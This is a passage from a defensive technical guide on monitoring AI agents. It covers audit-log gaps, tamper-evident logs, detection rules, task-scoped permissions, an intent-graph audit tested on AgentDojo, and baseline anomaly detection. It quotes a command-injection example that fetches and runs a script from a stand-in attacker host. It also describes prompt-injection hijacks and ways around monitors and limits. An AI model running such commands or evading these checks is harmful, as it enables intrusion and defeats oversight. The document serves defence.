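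Before some actions, Cursor waits for the hook to allow or deny them. Elastic's script always allows them, and it answers before it writes anything. A logging failure, such as a full disk, therefore doesn't interrupt the developer, but the action can go ahead without a record.

In the first two months after the company-wide rollout, Elastic collected over 13 million events from more than 1,100 machines and nearly 900 users. File reads outnumbered shell commands by roughly four to one, which surprised the team. Elastic had previously known only about the MCP servers that people remembered to mention, but it found more than 300 different ones in the log. Only one or two people used each of 86% of these servers.

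The two faults that took the team the most time produced no error messages. Cursor splits the path to a hook script at spaces, so a script in macOS's `Application Support` folder never ran. Cursor also reads its hook settings only when it starts. The developers had not restarted their editors, so no events arrived, even though Elastic's deployment tool showed every machine as green. The management software now detects when Cursor is running and asks the user to restart it.

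The first log format also caused trouble because it stored Cursor's original description of each event, with useful values up to three levels deep and in different places for different events. Elastic then changed the script to copy the tool name, command, file path and server name into their own fields. It also kept the original description, so when Cursor added new fields, the log already contained them.

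A developer with administrator rights can remove the hooks or edit the script, and on a Mac the user can change the log file before the forwarding program sends it. The agent runs under the same account, so a hijacked agent could do the same. Work under a personal Cursor login is not logged on machines that receive their hooks through the company's Cursor account. Elastic chose not to collect prompts, model responses or file contents. That made the project acceptable to its engineers, but an investigator who sees that an agent ran a command cannot see the text that led to it.

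### Microsoft Defender and Agent 365

A company whose agents run on a large vendor's platform can leave more of the collection to the vendor. Microsoft Defender XDR combines security data from machines, accounts and email, and it now receives data about agents from Agent 365, Microsoft's administration system for them. Scalzi (2026), in *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR*, lists the agents it covers:

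- agents that staff build with little code in Copilot Studio
- agents that developers build in Microsoft Foundry
- simpler agents that users build inside Microsoft 365 Copilot
- agents from elsewhere that use the Agent 365 development kit
- some coding and desktop agents on employees' machines

Each managed agent gets its own identity in Entra, Microsoft's account directory, with named owners, sign-in logs and a risk score. An analyst can then tell the agent's sign-ins from Maria's. Microsoft 365 Copilot is not on the list because Microsoft operates it. Its activity goes to Purview, a compliance product, and the customer can connect it to Sentinel, Microsoft's SIEM, as a separate step.

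The data is spread across several tables. According to Microsoft, `AgentsInfo` lists agents, `CopilotActivity` records Copilot use, `CloudAppEvents` holds verdicts on prompts (such as a suspected injection), `SecurityAlert` holds alerts, and `SecurityIncident` holds the incidents built from them. To find out what an agent did, who owned it and whether its input was malicious, an analyst has to combine at least three of these tables.

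Coverage also depends on licences and settings. A customer may need the Agent 365 add-on or a more expensive plan. The default rule for real-time protection only audits suspicious actions, and Scalzi recommends adding one that blocks them. On employees' machines, Defender reads data from hooks like those Elastic used, or inspects the network requests of agents without hooks. In November 2026 this feature was still in beta and supported Claude Code, Codex CLI, and GitHub Copilot's command-line tool and app, but not Cursor.

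### Finding agents that nobody registered

Neither Elastic's script nor Agent 365 would have revealed the second support agent that the shop's marketing department set up. Canale and Soulis studied how to find such agents on Windows laptops. An agent keeps a connection to an outside service and runs commands, but so does ordinary automation, so this behaviour alone doesn't identify an agent. They constructed "behavioural twins", in which the same script connects to a software package index instead of a model. The twin starts the same programs with the same timing, so a detector that ignores the identity of the outside service must flag both or neither.

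Their own detector starts from that identity. It checks which programs are connected to a service in its catalogue of model providers and resellers, and reports a probable agent if such a program has also started a command shell. It also looks for local models, configuration files and installed tools. They ran it on one workstation against 12 synthetic agents and 9 harmless workloads, including three twins, and repeated the test five times. These are the majority results:

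| Detector | Agents found (of 12) | Harmless workloads flagged (of 9) |
|---|---|---|
| Names of known agent programs | 0 | 0 |
| Script interpreter with a connection and a shell | 9 | 4 |
| Any program with a connection and a shell | 10 | 4 |
| Canale and Soulis's detector | 12 | 0 |

Both behavioural rules flagged all three twins and a routine software installation. This supports the argument about twins because the result follows from how the rules work, whatever the size of the test.

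The perfect score in the last row is much weaker evidence. Canale and Soulis had corrected the detector after seeing its mistakes on the same tests, and two of the 12 agents turned up in only three of the five runs. Every scan also ran within seconds of the agent starting, when it is easiest to identify. Many providers share network addresses with unrelated websites, so the detector has to rely on the name lookups that Windows stores for a few minutes. An agent that keeps its connection open does not repeat the lookup. In a separate test of 12 such connections, the detector could identify none of them after 295 seconds. It is designed to scan once an hour, so it would usually miss such connections.

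Of 40 scans run at random times, 15 detected an agent that connected only occasionally. The detector also missed an agent that reached its model through an unlisted intermediary, one that ran for only five seconds, and one inside WSL 2, the Linux environment on Windows. Microsoft's Sysmon tool can log name lookups and program starts continuously, which should catch the short-lived agent and avoid the problem of expired lookups. Canale and Soulis did not test this approach, and it produces far more data than an hourly scan.

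### Audit logs that left out agent actions

Microsoft has written that its Unified Audit Log captures every AI interaction, whether from Copilot or an unmanaged application, but at least two groups of researchers have found exceptions.

In July 2025, Zack Korman of the security company Pistachio asked Microsoft 365 Copilot to summarise a file but not link to it. Copilot supplied the summary, but the audit log showed no access to the file. Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won't Tell You* reports that he noticed the fault by chance while testing a product that reads the log. Ordinary users may therefore have caused the same gap by accident, and a departing employee could have used it to read confidential files without being logged.

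Microsoft classified the flaw as "important" and fixed it in August, but told Korman it had no plans to inform customers. Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had disclosed the same problem a year earlier. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) describes a retest with a similar prompt, in which the log listed the files. The fix does not add the missing accesses to older logs.

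This gap was especially serious because, when the Copilot record omitted a file, there was no second record from the system storing the file to reveal the omission. When a user opens a file directly, the log contains a file-access event from SharePoint, Microsoft's file store, but when Copilot opens it for the user, the log contains a Copilot interaction instead. Korman considers that correct, since the user did not open the file.

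Datadog, a monitoring company, found a different gap when its researchers created an agent in Copilot Studio, carried out the administrative actions that Microsoft's documentation lists as logged, and checked the logs 24 hours later. Datadog Security Labs' *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) reports that four kinds of change were missing: altering an agent's login requirement, changing its conversation logging, sharing it and publishing a new version. An attacker with editing rights could have opened the agent to anonymous users, switched off the conversation log and extracted the agent's data without leaving a record of the changes or the conversation.

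Microsoft had fixed all four by October 2025. In later tests, two were again logged only sometimes or not at all, and in March 2026 Microsoft said its engineers could not reproduce the problem. A successful test is therefore good evidence only that the audit log worked that day, so the customer has to repeat the test.

Vendors document other gaps themselves. In March 2026, activity in Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, did not appear in audit logs, data exports or the Compliance API, which customers use to retrieve records, according to Anthropic's *Use Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans*. Anthropic has since added Cowork and Claude Code to the API, but the beta excludes Claude Code on the web and sessions run through other cloud providers, according to its *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code*. OpenAI stated in a help page, still current in July 2026, that its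 Atlas browser, which includes an agent, sends no compliance logs and does not connect to a SIEM.

### Making alterations visible

An attacker who takes over an agent has reason to delete the records of how it happened. The shop's first protection is to move each record quickly to a store outside the agent's reach. It gives the harness a credential that can add records to this store but cannot read, change or delete them, and it gives the people who run the agent no administrator rights there. A hijacked agent may still be able to add false records, but the earlier ones stay. Some storage services also offer a time lock that stops even administrators from deleting a record before a set date.

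Long retention alone does not provide this protection. *Control 1.7*, a community guide to Microsoft's audit log, notes that paying for ten years of retention does not by itself meet the preservation rule for American broker-dealers. Firms can meet the rule with locked storage, among other options.

A hash chain makes changes visible if someone does get into the store. The program that writes the log computes a hash for each record from the record's content and the hash of the record before it. For three records from the lamp session, with invented hashes shortened to four characters, the chain could look like this:

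```
record  content                      previous hash  own hash
r-203   search_policy, damaged item  51d0           8ac4
r-204   issue_refund, 45.00 EUR      8ac4           3be8
r-205   send_message, to c-3071      3be8           f617
```

Suppose an intruder changes 45.00 to 15.00 in r-204. A checking program recomputes that record's hash and gets `c902`, which does not match the stored `3be8`. The intruder can replace `3be8` with `c902`, but r-205 still contains `3be8` as its previous hash, so the check fails there instead. To fix that, the intruder has to put `c902` into r-205, recompute that record's hash, and repeat the process for every later record in the log.

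Someone with full control of the store can alter a record and recompute the hashes that follow, leaving a chain without errors. The shop therefore has to copy the latest hash at regular intervals to a system that the intruder cannot write to. If it saved r-205's original hash, `f617`, elsewhere at 10:45, comparing it with the hash of the rewritten record will expose the change. The shop can also use the saved copy to detect that someone has deleted records from the end of the log, which the chain alone does not show.

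A hash can protect only what the program wrote. If the harness crashes after paying the refund but before writing r-204, it can restart and write r-205 with `8ac4` as the previous hash. All the hashes will match, although the log is missing the refund. A hash chain over Microsoft's audit log would likewise have confirmed the version without Korman's file as intact. OpenAI's *New compliance and administrative tools for ChatGPT Enterprise* (2024) describes the company's compliance exports as "immutable, time-windowed JSONL log files", and the same limit applies to them. Customers know that nobody has changed a finished file, but they need another source to check that it is complete.

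### Finding records that are missing

A heartbeat is a record that a program sends at fixed intervals even when nothing has happened. If the shop's harness sends one every minute, a five-minute gap in the records means that the harness, the connection or the logging has failed. Without a heartbeat, the same gap could mean that no customers had written. Canale and Soulis's detector writes one summary event per scan for this purpose.

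A laptop that is switched off also sends nothing, so a missing heartbeat is only suspicious if the machine is otherwise active. Elastic considers a machine worth investigating when its hook events stop but other activity continues. It also recommends comparing the log with an inventory from osquery, a tool that lists what is installed on each machine. This finds machines that have the agent but have never sent an event, which would include any where the developer had not restarted Cursor.

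Heartbeats show that the logging program is running, but not that it records every action. To check that, the shop has to compare the harness's log with the payment ledger. Each night it can take all refunds under the agent's account from the ledger and look for the matching harness records. It should match them by individual payment identifier, because the totals can be equal even when one record is missing and another is false.

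If a refund appears only in the ledger, the harness may have lost the record, or someone may have used the agent's credentials outside the harness, which would be a serious incident. If a refund appears only in the harness's log, it may have failed after the payment system accepted it. Some mismatches will be caused by late records, so the check has to allow for the slowest log. Datadog waited a full day before it concluded that Microsoft's events were missing.

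Reconciliation works well for payments and emails, which other systems record anyway, but poorly for reads. If the agent looks up a customer's address, a second record exists only if the database logs reads, and many databases do not by default. For such actions, the shop can regularly perform a known action and check that the expected record arrives, as Datadog did.

### Legal duties and logs that expire

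The EU AI Act (Regulation 2024/1689) contains the most direct legal duties to log, but only for systems it classes as high-risk. Article 12 requires these systems to be technically able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The recorded events must help to identify risks and substantial modifications, and allow both the provider and the deployer (the organisation using the system) to monitor the system's operation. The article prescribes specific log contents only for remote biometric identification, so it does not specify which fields an agent's record needs.

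Article 19 requires providers to keep the logs under their control, and Article 26 requires deployers to do the same. Both must keep them for a period that suits the system's purpose and is at least six months, unless other law, in particular data protection law, provides otherwise.

These duties do not apply yet because an amending law, the Digital Omnibus, postponed them when it entered into force on 27 July 2026, as the National Law Review reported in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026). They will apply from 2 December 2027 to systems in listed fields such as recruitment, education and credit scoring, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in regulated products such as medical devices. The shop's refund agent falls into neither group, but an agent the shop used to rank job applicants would normally be high-risk.

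Default retention periods can be much shorter than six months. Microsoft's log store keeps table data for 30 days unless the customer changes the setting. Microsoft's *Enable Diagnostic Logging for AI Services and Agents* calls this insufficient for most investigations and recommends 90 to 180 days of searchable data, with cheaper storage for up to 12 years in total. Microsoft says it keeps audit records of other companies' AI applications for 180 days. Six calendar months last 181 to 184 days, so a deployer relying on such a log alone would miss the Act's minimum by one to four days.

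In Help Net Security's *Shadow AI incident response begins with logs that may already be gone*, Brandy Wityak, who investigates incidents at the security company LevelBlue, says that firewall records of connections to AI services are usually the first to disappear. These records are often the clearest evidence of what data left the company, but they are frequently gone by the time her team arrives. Clients have repeatedly taken three days to look for a log, then reported that they couldn't find it or had never stored it. She is drawing on experience and gives no counts, but her account is consistent with the faults that Elastic and Datadog found in logs they had reason to think were working. A company that suspects an incident should therefore pause automatic log deletion before it starts to investigate.

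Switching on logging later also does not recover earlier events. Anthropic's *Compliance API 常见问题*, a page of frequently asked questions, explains that Anthropic keeps the API's activity feed for six years, but that the feed starts when the customer first enables the API and does not include earlier events. Retention periods need to match. If the shop keeps its payment ledger for ten years and its harness log for 30 days, then after 30 days it can still prove that the agent paid a refund but can no longer find out why.

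## Detecting incidents with rules and declared task limits

Detection rules need no history of the agent's behaviour, so they work from its first day, even on a copy that runs for only a few minutes. The simplest rules check a single record. *MCP security risks*, a Datadog guide by Mooney, gives the example of a ticket search whose query ends with `; curl attacker.com/script | bash`. On a carelessly written server, everything after the semicolon runs as a new command. Ordinary searches rarely contain a semicolon, so a rule can check for one.

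Many attacks on the shop's agent would leave no such mark in any one record. Microsoft (2026) warns that an attacker who influences an agent's plan can cause harm without exceeding the agent's permissions. The SIEM can detect such attacks only by correlating several records.

### Three rules for the support agent

The shop could start with a rule for a sensitive read followed by an external send:

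```
RULE  sensitive read, then external send
find  read = a successful get_customer
then  send = a successful send_message
in    the same trace
where send.customer_id is not read.customer_id
```

The support agent routinely writes to people outside the company, so "external" here means anyone other than the customer whose details the agent has just read. The rule would catch the man who talked the agent into emailing him another customer's address. It would also flag harmless gift orders, in which the agent looks up the recipient and then writes to the buyer. It would miss a leak through `get_order`. If the agent read only the order and quoted a delivery note containing the recipient's door code, there would be no `get_customer` call for the rule to match.

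Microsoft describes the same pattern in an office agent. An insider hides instructions in a shared document, and the agent reads a transaction file that the insider cannot open, then tries to email it to an outside address. The rule would miss another of Microsoft's scenarios, in which an attacker questions a public support chatbot that has customer data in its knowledge base, because the data can leave in the chatbot's replies without any call to an email tool.

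Several companies have published rules of this kind. Invariant Labs' *Dataflow Rules* describes an arrow operator that matches one event followed by another in an agent's trace. In one of the company's examples, the arrow connects a call that reads the user's inbox to an email sent outside the company. The pattern for outside addresses is faulty because its square brackets make it check only whether the first character after the @ sign is one of the letters in `ourcompany.com`. It therefore matches gmail.com but not outlook.com or yahoo.com. A company that copied the rule should test it with messages that ought to raise an alert.

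Elastic's rule *GenAI Process Performing Encoding/Chunking Prior to Network Activity* covers coding agents on laptops. It looks for an AI tool starting a program to encode or compress data, followed within 30 seconds by a connection to an outside address. Version 1 of the query requires the same process to do both. A Python script can do that, but `gzip` doesn't open network connections, so the rule would miss an agent that compressed a file with `gzip` and uploaded it with `curl`.

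A rule that checks only for a sensitive read, or only for a suspicious send, is rarely enough. When Elastic searched its own logs for agents that read credential files, it found that agents constantly read `.env` files, because developers keep connection settings there. Requiring a suspicious send as well removes most of these matches. Where documents carry sensitivity labels, a rule can use them to identify sensitive data. For example, a query on KQL Search, a site that collects searches for Microsoft's security products, looks for Copilot output that came from a highly confidential source and then lost its label or went to a less trusted destination, such as a personal email account.

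A different rule catches calls that belong to no piece of work:

```
RULE   call without an open task
find   call = any action under the support agent's account
unless the ticket system has a task where
       task.id = call.task_id
       and the task was open at call.time
```

Suppose someone finds the agent's password in a configuration file and uses it to send €95 to their own card. The payment system records a payment that belongs to no open task, so the rule matches. The shop should take the list of tasks from the ticket system, because a thief can write any task number into a request. The rule might also match harmlessly if the agent's closing email leaves a few seconds after the ticket system marks the case as closed. A one-minute grace period would remove most of these harmless matches.

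The rule is weak against anyone who can create a task, and anyone who can email a shop can create one. A thief can open a task by first complaining about a broken lamp. A hijacked agent also has an open task when it follows a hidden instruction while serving an honest customer.

Van den Daele's *Hunt for AI Agent activity with Agent Info* includes a search that joins Microsoft's activity log to its register of agents, so an analyst can see what each registered agent did. The shop would have to write a similar join to its ticket system, to fit that system's fields.

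The last of the three looks for an agent that keeps trying until something works:

```
RULE  refused several times, then done another way
find  3 or more denied calls in one trace within 10 minutes
then  a successful call
where it concerns the same order
and   its tool or arguments differ from the denied calls
and   it has no approval_id
```

Suppose a hidden instruction tells the agent to refund €180. The permission layer refuses its attempts at €180, €150 and €120. The agent then pays €90 twice on the same order, and the first payment triggers the alert. But the same rule would flag an agent that tries three times to refund €140 for two lamps, checks the policy, sees that the customer returned only one, and correctly pays €70. And if the €100 limit is in the system prompt, a hijacked agent may split the €180 from the start and get no refusals. To catch that, the shop would need another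 rule that adds up the refunds on each order.

Most published rules cover only refused actions. Elastic's *AWS Bedrock Detected Multiple Attempts to use Denied Models* counts access denials and lists any user with more than three for the same model. Google Cloud's *Agent Platform Threat Detection overview* includes a detector for agents that repeatedly trigger permission errors across several services, and rates its findings as medium severity. Mooney recommends an alert when calls returning the web error codes 401 or 500 suddenly increase. A server that recognises the caller but refuses the action normally returns 403, so the shop would have to add that code to the alert.

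Repeated refusals are weaker evidence of an attacker than they used to be. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers*, an analysis of a week of data from customers' Windows machines in June 2026, describes how OpenAI's coding agent Codex tried to download a legitimate Python installer from python.org. Codex used `certutil`, a Windows tool that attackers often misuse for downloads. When Sophos' software blocked several attempts, Codex switched to `bitsadmin`, another such tool, and the software blocked that too. The shop's rule would not have matched, because neither tool succeeded, but it would have if Codex had found a third tool that Sophos allowed. Sophos observes that this switching used to separate a human attacker from a simple script, and that harmless agents now do it routinely.

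### Limits for each task

A company can declare what the current task needs and treat everything else as a violation, instead of listing dangerous patterns. For example, an agent that answers a question about a delivery needs `get_order` and `send_message`. If it issues a refund in that session, that is a violation, even though its account has permission to issue refunds.

Hagverdiyev (2026), in *Compromise Is Not Consequence*, measured what such limits achieve when a person writes them correctly. The test used five small models and 128 scenarios involving files, calendars, mail and payments. Each model read text containing a malicious instruction. Hagverdiyev then recorded the model's next request and sent it unchanged to the service under a broad credential and under three credentials limited to the task. With the broad credential, 8.9% to 37.8% of decisions led to a harmful action, depending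 on the model. With the limited credentials, none did, and the service refused none of the requests that the task permitted.

The zero is expected, because the limits excluded the attacks by design and ordinary code enforced them. The experiment is more useful for showing that the models still chose actions outside their task. They did so 2,054 times, and the limits only prevented the service from carrying those actions out. Each refusal is therefore a good signal for the SIEM, because it may mean that someone has planted instructions in the agent's input. Later instructions may stay within the limits, and the service would not refuse them.

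The shop has few kinds of task, so it could write the limits for each by hand, but it would still have trouble with a customer who asks about a delivery and then mentions that last week's lamp was broken. A general office assistant receives too many kinds of request for hand-written limits, so a model has to predict them from the text of the task.

In *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, Noyan (2026) tested models that choose an agent's permissions for each task, using 100 tasks from a fictional company and 15 possible permissions. A small model that Noyan trained for this withheld at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks and granted at least one unnecessary permission in 23%. Claude Haiku 4.5, given only a few examples, withheld a necessary permission in 11% of tasks but granted an unnecessary one in 42%. Noyan had decided beforehand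 that a usable system must withhold necessary permissions in fewer than 10% of tasks and reach a precision of at least 0.90. Neither model met both conditions at any of the six settings tested.

### Shavit's intent-graph audit

A list of tools does not limit what the agent does with them. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, November 2026) presents a more detailed check. Shavit works at the security company Silverfort.

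Before the agent starts, a language model receives the user's objective, the agent's system prompt and the full list of tools. It writes a plan, which Shavit calls an intent graph, with the tools for each step, limits on their arguments and the order of the steps. For the broken lamp, the plan might look like this:

```
step 1  get_order      order_id = 88213
step 2  search_policy
step 3  issue_refund   order_id = 88213       after step 1
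step 4  send_message   customer_id = c-3071   after step 3
```

The model may limit an argument only if the objective determines its value. The customer gave an order number but no price, so the plan leaves the amount open. The model may require steps to run in a particular sequence only if one step needs another's result or the user asked for that sequence. It writes the plan in a median of 3.6 seconds, without access to tool results, so a malicious delivery note cannot add steps.

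From then on, ordinary code checks each tool call against the plan, in a median of 5.7 millionths of a second:

1. It blocks the call if the tool is not in the plan or if an earlier step is still missing.
2. It flags the call if the arguments break the plan's limits.
3. It works out which later steps the call would unlock, and blocks it if they include a serious administrative action. This check never caught a malicious call in Shavit's tests.
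4. It flags the call if its arguments repeat text from a call that failed a check in the previous 30 seconds.

If a hidden instruction told the agent to refund the customer's last five purchases, the other order numbers would violate the limit in step 3. An instruction to refund €95 for the €45 lamp would pass, because the plan does not set the amount. Such gaps are common. In Shavit's plans, 61% of the steps left the arguments unrestricted.

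The method also depends on a trustworthy objective. That is reasonable for an assistant that works for its owner, but the shop's agent takes requests from strangers. If a thief asks for refunds on five orders, the model will write a plan with five refunds. The shop would do better to build the plan from its own task type and the order number in the ticket.

Shavit tested the audit on AgentDojo, a public benchmark in which agents handle email, banking, travel and messaging tasks while some of the text they read contains malicious instructions. The test used stored logs from the May 2024 version of GPT-4o, with one harmless run of each of 97 tasks and 629 runs with injected instructions. Shavit used 21 tasks for development and reported the main results on the other 76.

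On those tasks, the attack succeeded in 45.7% of the runs without a defence and in 3.3% with the full audit. The lower figure counts an attack as stopped if the audit would have flagged the first malicious call. The audit also flagged 40% of the harmless tasks. An attack often begins with a harmless lookup, such as an email search, so Shavit also counted whether the audit would have flagged the first call that could do damage. The table gives both measures:

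| Checks applied | Attack success, first malicious call | Attack success, first damaging call | Harmless tasks flagged | Harmless tasks blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 45.7% | 45.7% | – | – |
| Tools | 10.2% | 9.6% | 16.2% | 16.2% |
| Tools and arguments | 5.5% | 4.3% | 32.9% | 16.2% |
| Full audit, including order | 3.3% | 2.0% | 40.4% | 31.1% |
| Tools and arguments, local reads exempt | 13.4% | 4.3% | 25.4% | 8.8% |
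| Full audit, local reads exempt | 11.4% | 2.0% | 31.6% | 23.2% |

The flagged column includes the blocked tasks. Most of the protection comes from the list of tools. The rules about order lower attack success by a further 2.2 percentage points on either measure, but they nearly double the share of harmless tasks that the audit blocks.

Many of the false alarms concerned simple lookups, so Shavit exempted 44 tools, out of 69, that only read the user's own data. This did not change attack success at the damaging step, and with checks on tools and arguments alone, the share of harmless tasks blocked fell from 16.2% to 8.8%. The tool that opens web pages still needed checks, because an agent can send data out inside a web address. Exempting it raised attack success at the damaging step under the full audit from 2.0% to 5.8%. At the shop, this approach would leave only refunds and emails to check,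 which would be worthwhile as long as reading a customer's details does no harm by itself.

Shavit then had a second model review each flagged call. This model received the objective, the plan and the earlier calls, but no tool results, so text planted in a document could not reach it directly. An attacker's words could still reach it if the agent copied them into a call, and Shavit did not test attacks designed to exploit this. With tools and arguments checked and local reads exempt, the review reduced the share of harmless tasks flagged from 27.6% to 21.1%. The starting figure differs from the table because Shavit ran the review on only one of three sets of plans. The model released 7 of 28 harmless calls and none of 226 harmful ones, and took about 3.6 seconds per call. A customer in a chat would hardly notice the delay, but a person would still need to check about one harmless task in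 five.

At least 15% of the harmless tasks needed a tool that the plan had left out. Noyan used different models and data and found withheld permissions in 11% to 21% of tasks. The similarity may be partly coincidence, but both results suggest that a short task description often does not reveal everything the agent will need.

AgentDojo's tool filter, a simpler defence, came close to the audit's results. Before the agent starts, a model chooses the relevant tools, and the agent is given only those. In live runs on the same tasks, attacks succeeded 6.5% of the time, and the agent completed 69.7% of the harmless tasks, compared with 67.1% without a defence. Shavit does not claim that the audit is better than the filter.

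The audit's figures come from replays, in which Shavit applied the checks to calls the agent had already made. A live agent might get around a refusal, so the replays probably overstate the protection. It might also find another way to finish a harmless task after a refusal, so the replays may overstate the disruption too.

The logged agent is also old. In a small live pilot with GPT-5.2, the agent read the malicious text in all 20 runs but never followed the injection. Shavit did not run the pilot with the audit switched on, because there were no successful attacks for it to stop. Twenty runs is a small sample, since an agent that obeyed one injection in ten would still have about a 12% chance of resisting all 20. The pilot also reused the attack from the old logs. The reduction from 45.7% to 3.3% is therefore good evidence about an agent that is easy to mislead, but weak evidence of how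 often the audit would stop an attack on a current one.

### Permission and habit

A correlation rule or a task limit tests whether the agent is allowed to do something in the circumstances, while a baseline measures how usual the action is. KQL Search has a query for Microsoft 365 Copilot that combines the two tests and shows why it matters to keep them separate. The query compares each agent's use of tools over 24 hours with its previous 14 days. It discards every approved tool, then lists the remaining ones only if they are new to the agent or their use is at least five times the baseline. The query therefore omits an unapproved tool that the agent has used at a steady rate for two weeks, as well as an approved tool that the agent suddenly calls a hundred times as often.

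Suppose the shop starts selling garden furniture. A customer returns a bench, and the agent refunds €98 to her card. The order number matches, the task is a return and the amount is within the limit, so neither the rules nor the plan would stop it. But the agent has never refunded more than €60 before, so a baseline would probably flag the payment, which would be a false positive. If a hidden instruction had instead raised a €45 refund to €98, the payment would be just as unusual and still within the limit, and the same alert would be useful. The shop could also write a rule that compares each refund with the price of the item, but someone would have to think of that check first.

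The thief with the stolen customer account would pass both tests, because a €45 refund for a broken lamp is permitted and routine. Shavit simulated a similar case, in which another person takes over mid-session. The audit did no better than chance (AUROC 0.48), because the new person's requests defined the new tasks. Behavioural detectors, which Shavit tested separately, did only modestly better. Detecting the thief would require evidence about the person making the request, such as the password reset.

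## Detecting anomalies against a baseline of normal behaviour

A baseline needs less foresight than a rule, because it only describes what the agent usually does and treats whatever looks different as worth checking. The case for it has three premises:

1. An agent's normal behaviour is stable enough to describe from its past logs.
2. Harmful behaviour departs from that description.
3. Departures are rare enough for analysts to inspect them.

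A security team can find attacks of a kind that nobody has seen before if the agent's normal behaviour is stable, the attacks depart from it, and the team can review all the unusual sessions. But an agent's work may change every week, a thief may ask for an ordinary refund, and a shop may have 300 unusual sessions a day, more than its team can read.

### From user profiles to system calls

In *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987), Dorothy Denning hypothesised that anyone who exploits a weakness in a computer system has to use the system abnormally. She therefore proposed keeping a statistical profile of each user and reporting deviations from it. UEBA products still work on this principle.

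Programs turned out to be easier to profile than people. In *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996) recorded system calls, the requests a running program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file. They chose programs with full rights over the machine because these do only a limited range of things. For their main test, they sent the mail-delivery program `sendmail` 112 messages designed to cover its normal variations, such as long, forwarded and bounced mail, and noted which calls followed which within a window of six. The messages produced over 1.5 million system calls, but about 1,500 entries were enough to describe them. Between 5% and 32% of the call sequences from seven other programs did not match this description.

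The method has limits that matter for agents. A baseline is valid for one version and configuration of a program, so a model update could make the shop's baseline obsolete. Forrest and colleagues also ignored the arguments of each call, which is where an attack on an agent often lies. They expected the method to have trouble detecting an intruder who logs in with someone else's password, as the thief with the stolen customer account does.

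The shop would also have to decide where its examples of normal behaviour come from. Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji (1998), in *Intrusion Detection using Sequences of System Calls*, collected them both by exercising a program artificially and by recording it in live use. Prepared customer messages would give the shop a baseline before the agent's first day, but only for the requests its staff thought of. Live logs include the requests customers actually make, but they may also include an attack, which then becomes part of the baseline.

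Sommer and Paxson (2010) made the best-known objection to anomaly detection. They observed that companies rarely used machine learning to detect intrusions in network traffic, despite years of research, and argued that finding attacks is fundamentally different from the tasks at which machine learning succeeds. A spam filter learns from examples of both spam and ordinary mail, whereas an anomaly detector has examples only of normal behaviour and must recognise everything else. Mistakes also do more harm. A bad book recommendation barely affects a shop, but every false alarm takes an analyst's time. Harmless network traffic also varies enormously, so an unusual event may be an attack or something as ordinary as a new printer. None of these difficulties is specific to network traffic.

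### Counts and timing in a sliding window

The most direct way to build a baseline is to count. A detector that Shavit tested takes the last 20 tool calls and computes each tool's share of them, how varied each tool's arguments were, and four statistics about the time between calls. For the shop's five tools, that makes 14 numbers, which the detector recomputes after each new call.

The detector then needs one score for how unusual the numbers are together. Shavit uses the Mahalanobis distance:

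```
D(x) = sqrt( (x − μ)ᵀ (Σ + λI)⁻¹ (x − μ) )
```

Here x is the list of numbers for the current window, and μ is their past average. Σ is the covariance matrix, which measures how much each number normally varies and how much the numbers vary together. I is the identity matrix, and λ is a small constant. Without λ, the matrix could not be inverted if the agent had never called one of the tools, because that tool's count would never have varied.

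Suppose the shop uses only two features, the number of policy searches and of refunds in the last 20 calls. In the past these averaged 4 and 3, each with a standard deviation of 1. Their correlation is 0.8, because the agent usually searches the policy before it issues a refund.

| Window | Policy searches | Refunds | Distance, λ = 0 | Distance, λ = 0.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Many returns | 6 | 5 | 2.1 | 2.1 |
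| Refunds without searches | 2 | 5 | 6.3 | 5.2 |

Each count is two standard deviations from its average in both windows, so a detector that checked one count at a time would score the windows the same. The Mahalanobis distance separates them because policy searches and refunds normally rise together. With λ = 0, the squared distance for the first window is (4 + 4 − 2 × 0.8 × 4) / (1 − 0.8²), or about 4.4. In the second window, the deviations have opposite signs, so the 2 × 0.8 × 4 term is added instead of subtracted, and the squared distance is 40.

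An analyst has to open the trace to find out what caused the score of 6.3. A hidden instruction may have made the agent pay, or the agent may have become careless about the policy. Alternatively, a courier may have lost a van full of parcels, and the agent may have looked up the rule once before handling five identical claims.

### The order of calls

Counts ignore order, which Forrest's method captures. The shop could apply it by recording which call comes next and which comes after that. Learned from a single normal session, the description would look like this:

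```
normal session: get_order, search_policy, issue_refund, send_message

call            next call        call after that
get_order       search_policy    issue_refund
search_policy   issue_refund     send_message
issue_refund    send_message     –
```

An agent that skips the policy search calls `get_order`, `issue_refund` and `send_message`. Two of that session's three pairs of calls are not in the table. An agent that searches the policy first and then reads the order does nothing wrong, but four of its five pairs are missing from the table, so it scores worse.

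Adding this harmless session to the table would remedy this, but the table would then contain all three pairs from the session without a policy search, so the omission would no longer produce a mismatch. Treating the start of a session as a call would restore one mismatch. Forrest and colleagues warned that too much variety in normal behaviour would make anomalies undetectable, and in this example a single variation almost does.

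*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that tries to learn which variations are harmless. One of its test agents takes a patient's symptoms, calls two tools to interpret them, and then looks up a checklist for each relevant hospital department. A patient with ankle pain and anxiety may be sent to orthopaedics and then psychiatry, or the other way round. Because both orders appear in past traces, the system treats the order of departments as unimportant and puts the department tools on the same level. It then splits each trace into units that contain only one department.

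A language model summarises the circumstances in which each unit is normal, for example that knee or arm pain leads to orthopaedics. TraceAegis flags a new trace if it contains an unfamiliar unit, such as a department lookup before anyone has interpreted the symptoms. It also flags a familiar unit in the wrong circumstances, such as foot pain leading to the ear, nose and throat department.

The team tested TraceAegis on this clinic agent and on an agent that submits purchase requests, with 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal traces for each. Using DeepSeek-V3, TraceAegis caught 96% of the abnormal traces from the clinic agent and 93% from the purchasing agent. The same model without the learned constraints caught 78% and 76%. The published precision and accuracy imply that TraceAegis also flagged about 3% of harmless clinic traces and 7% of harmless purchasing traces. Without the levels, precision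 on the clinic agent fell from 97% to 65% because the summaries mixed several departments into one confused rule.

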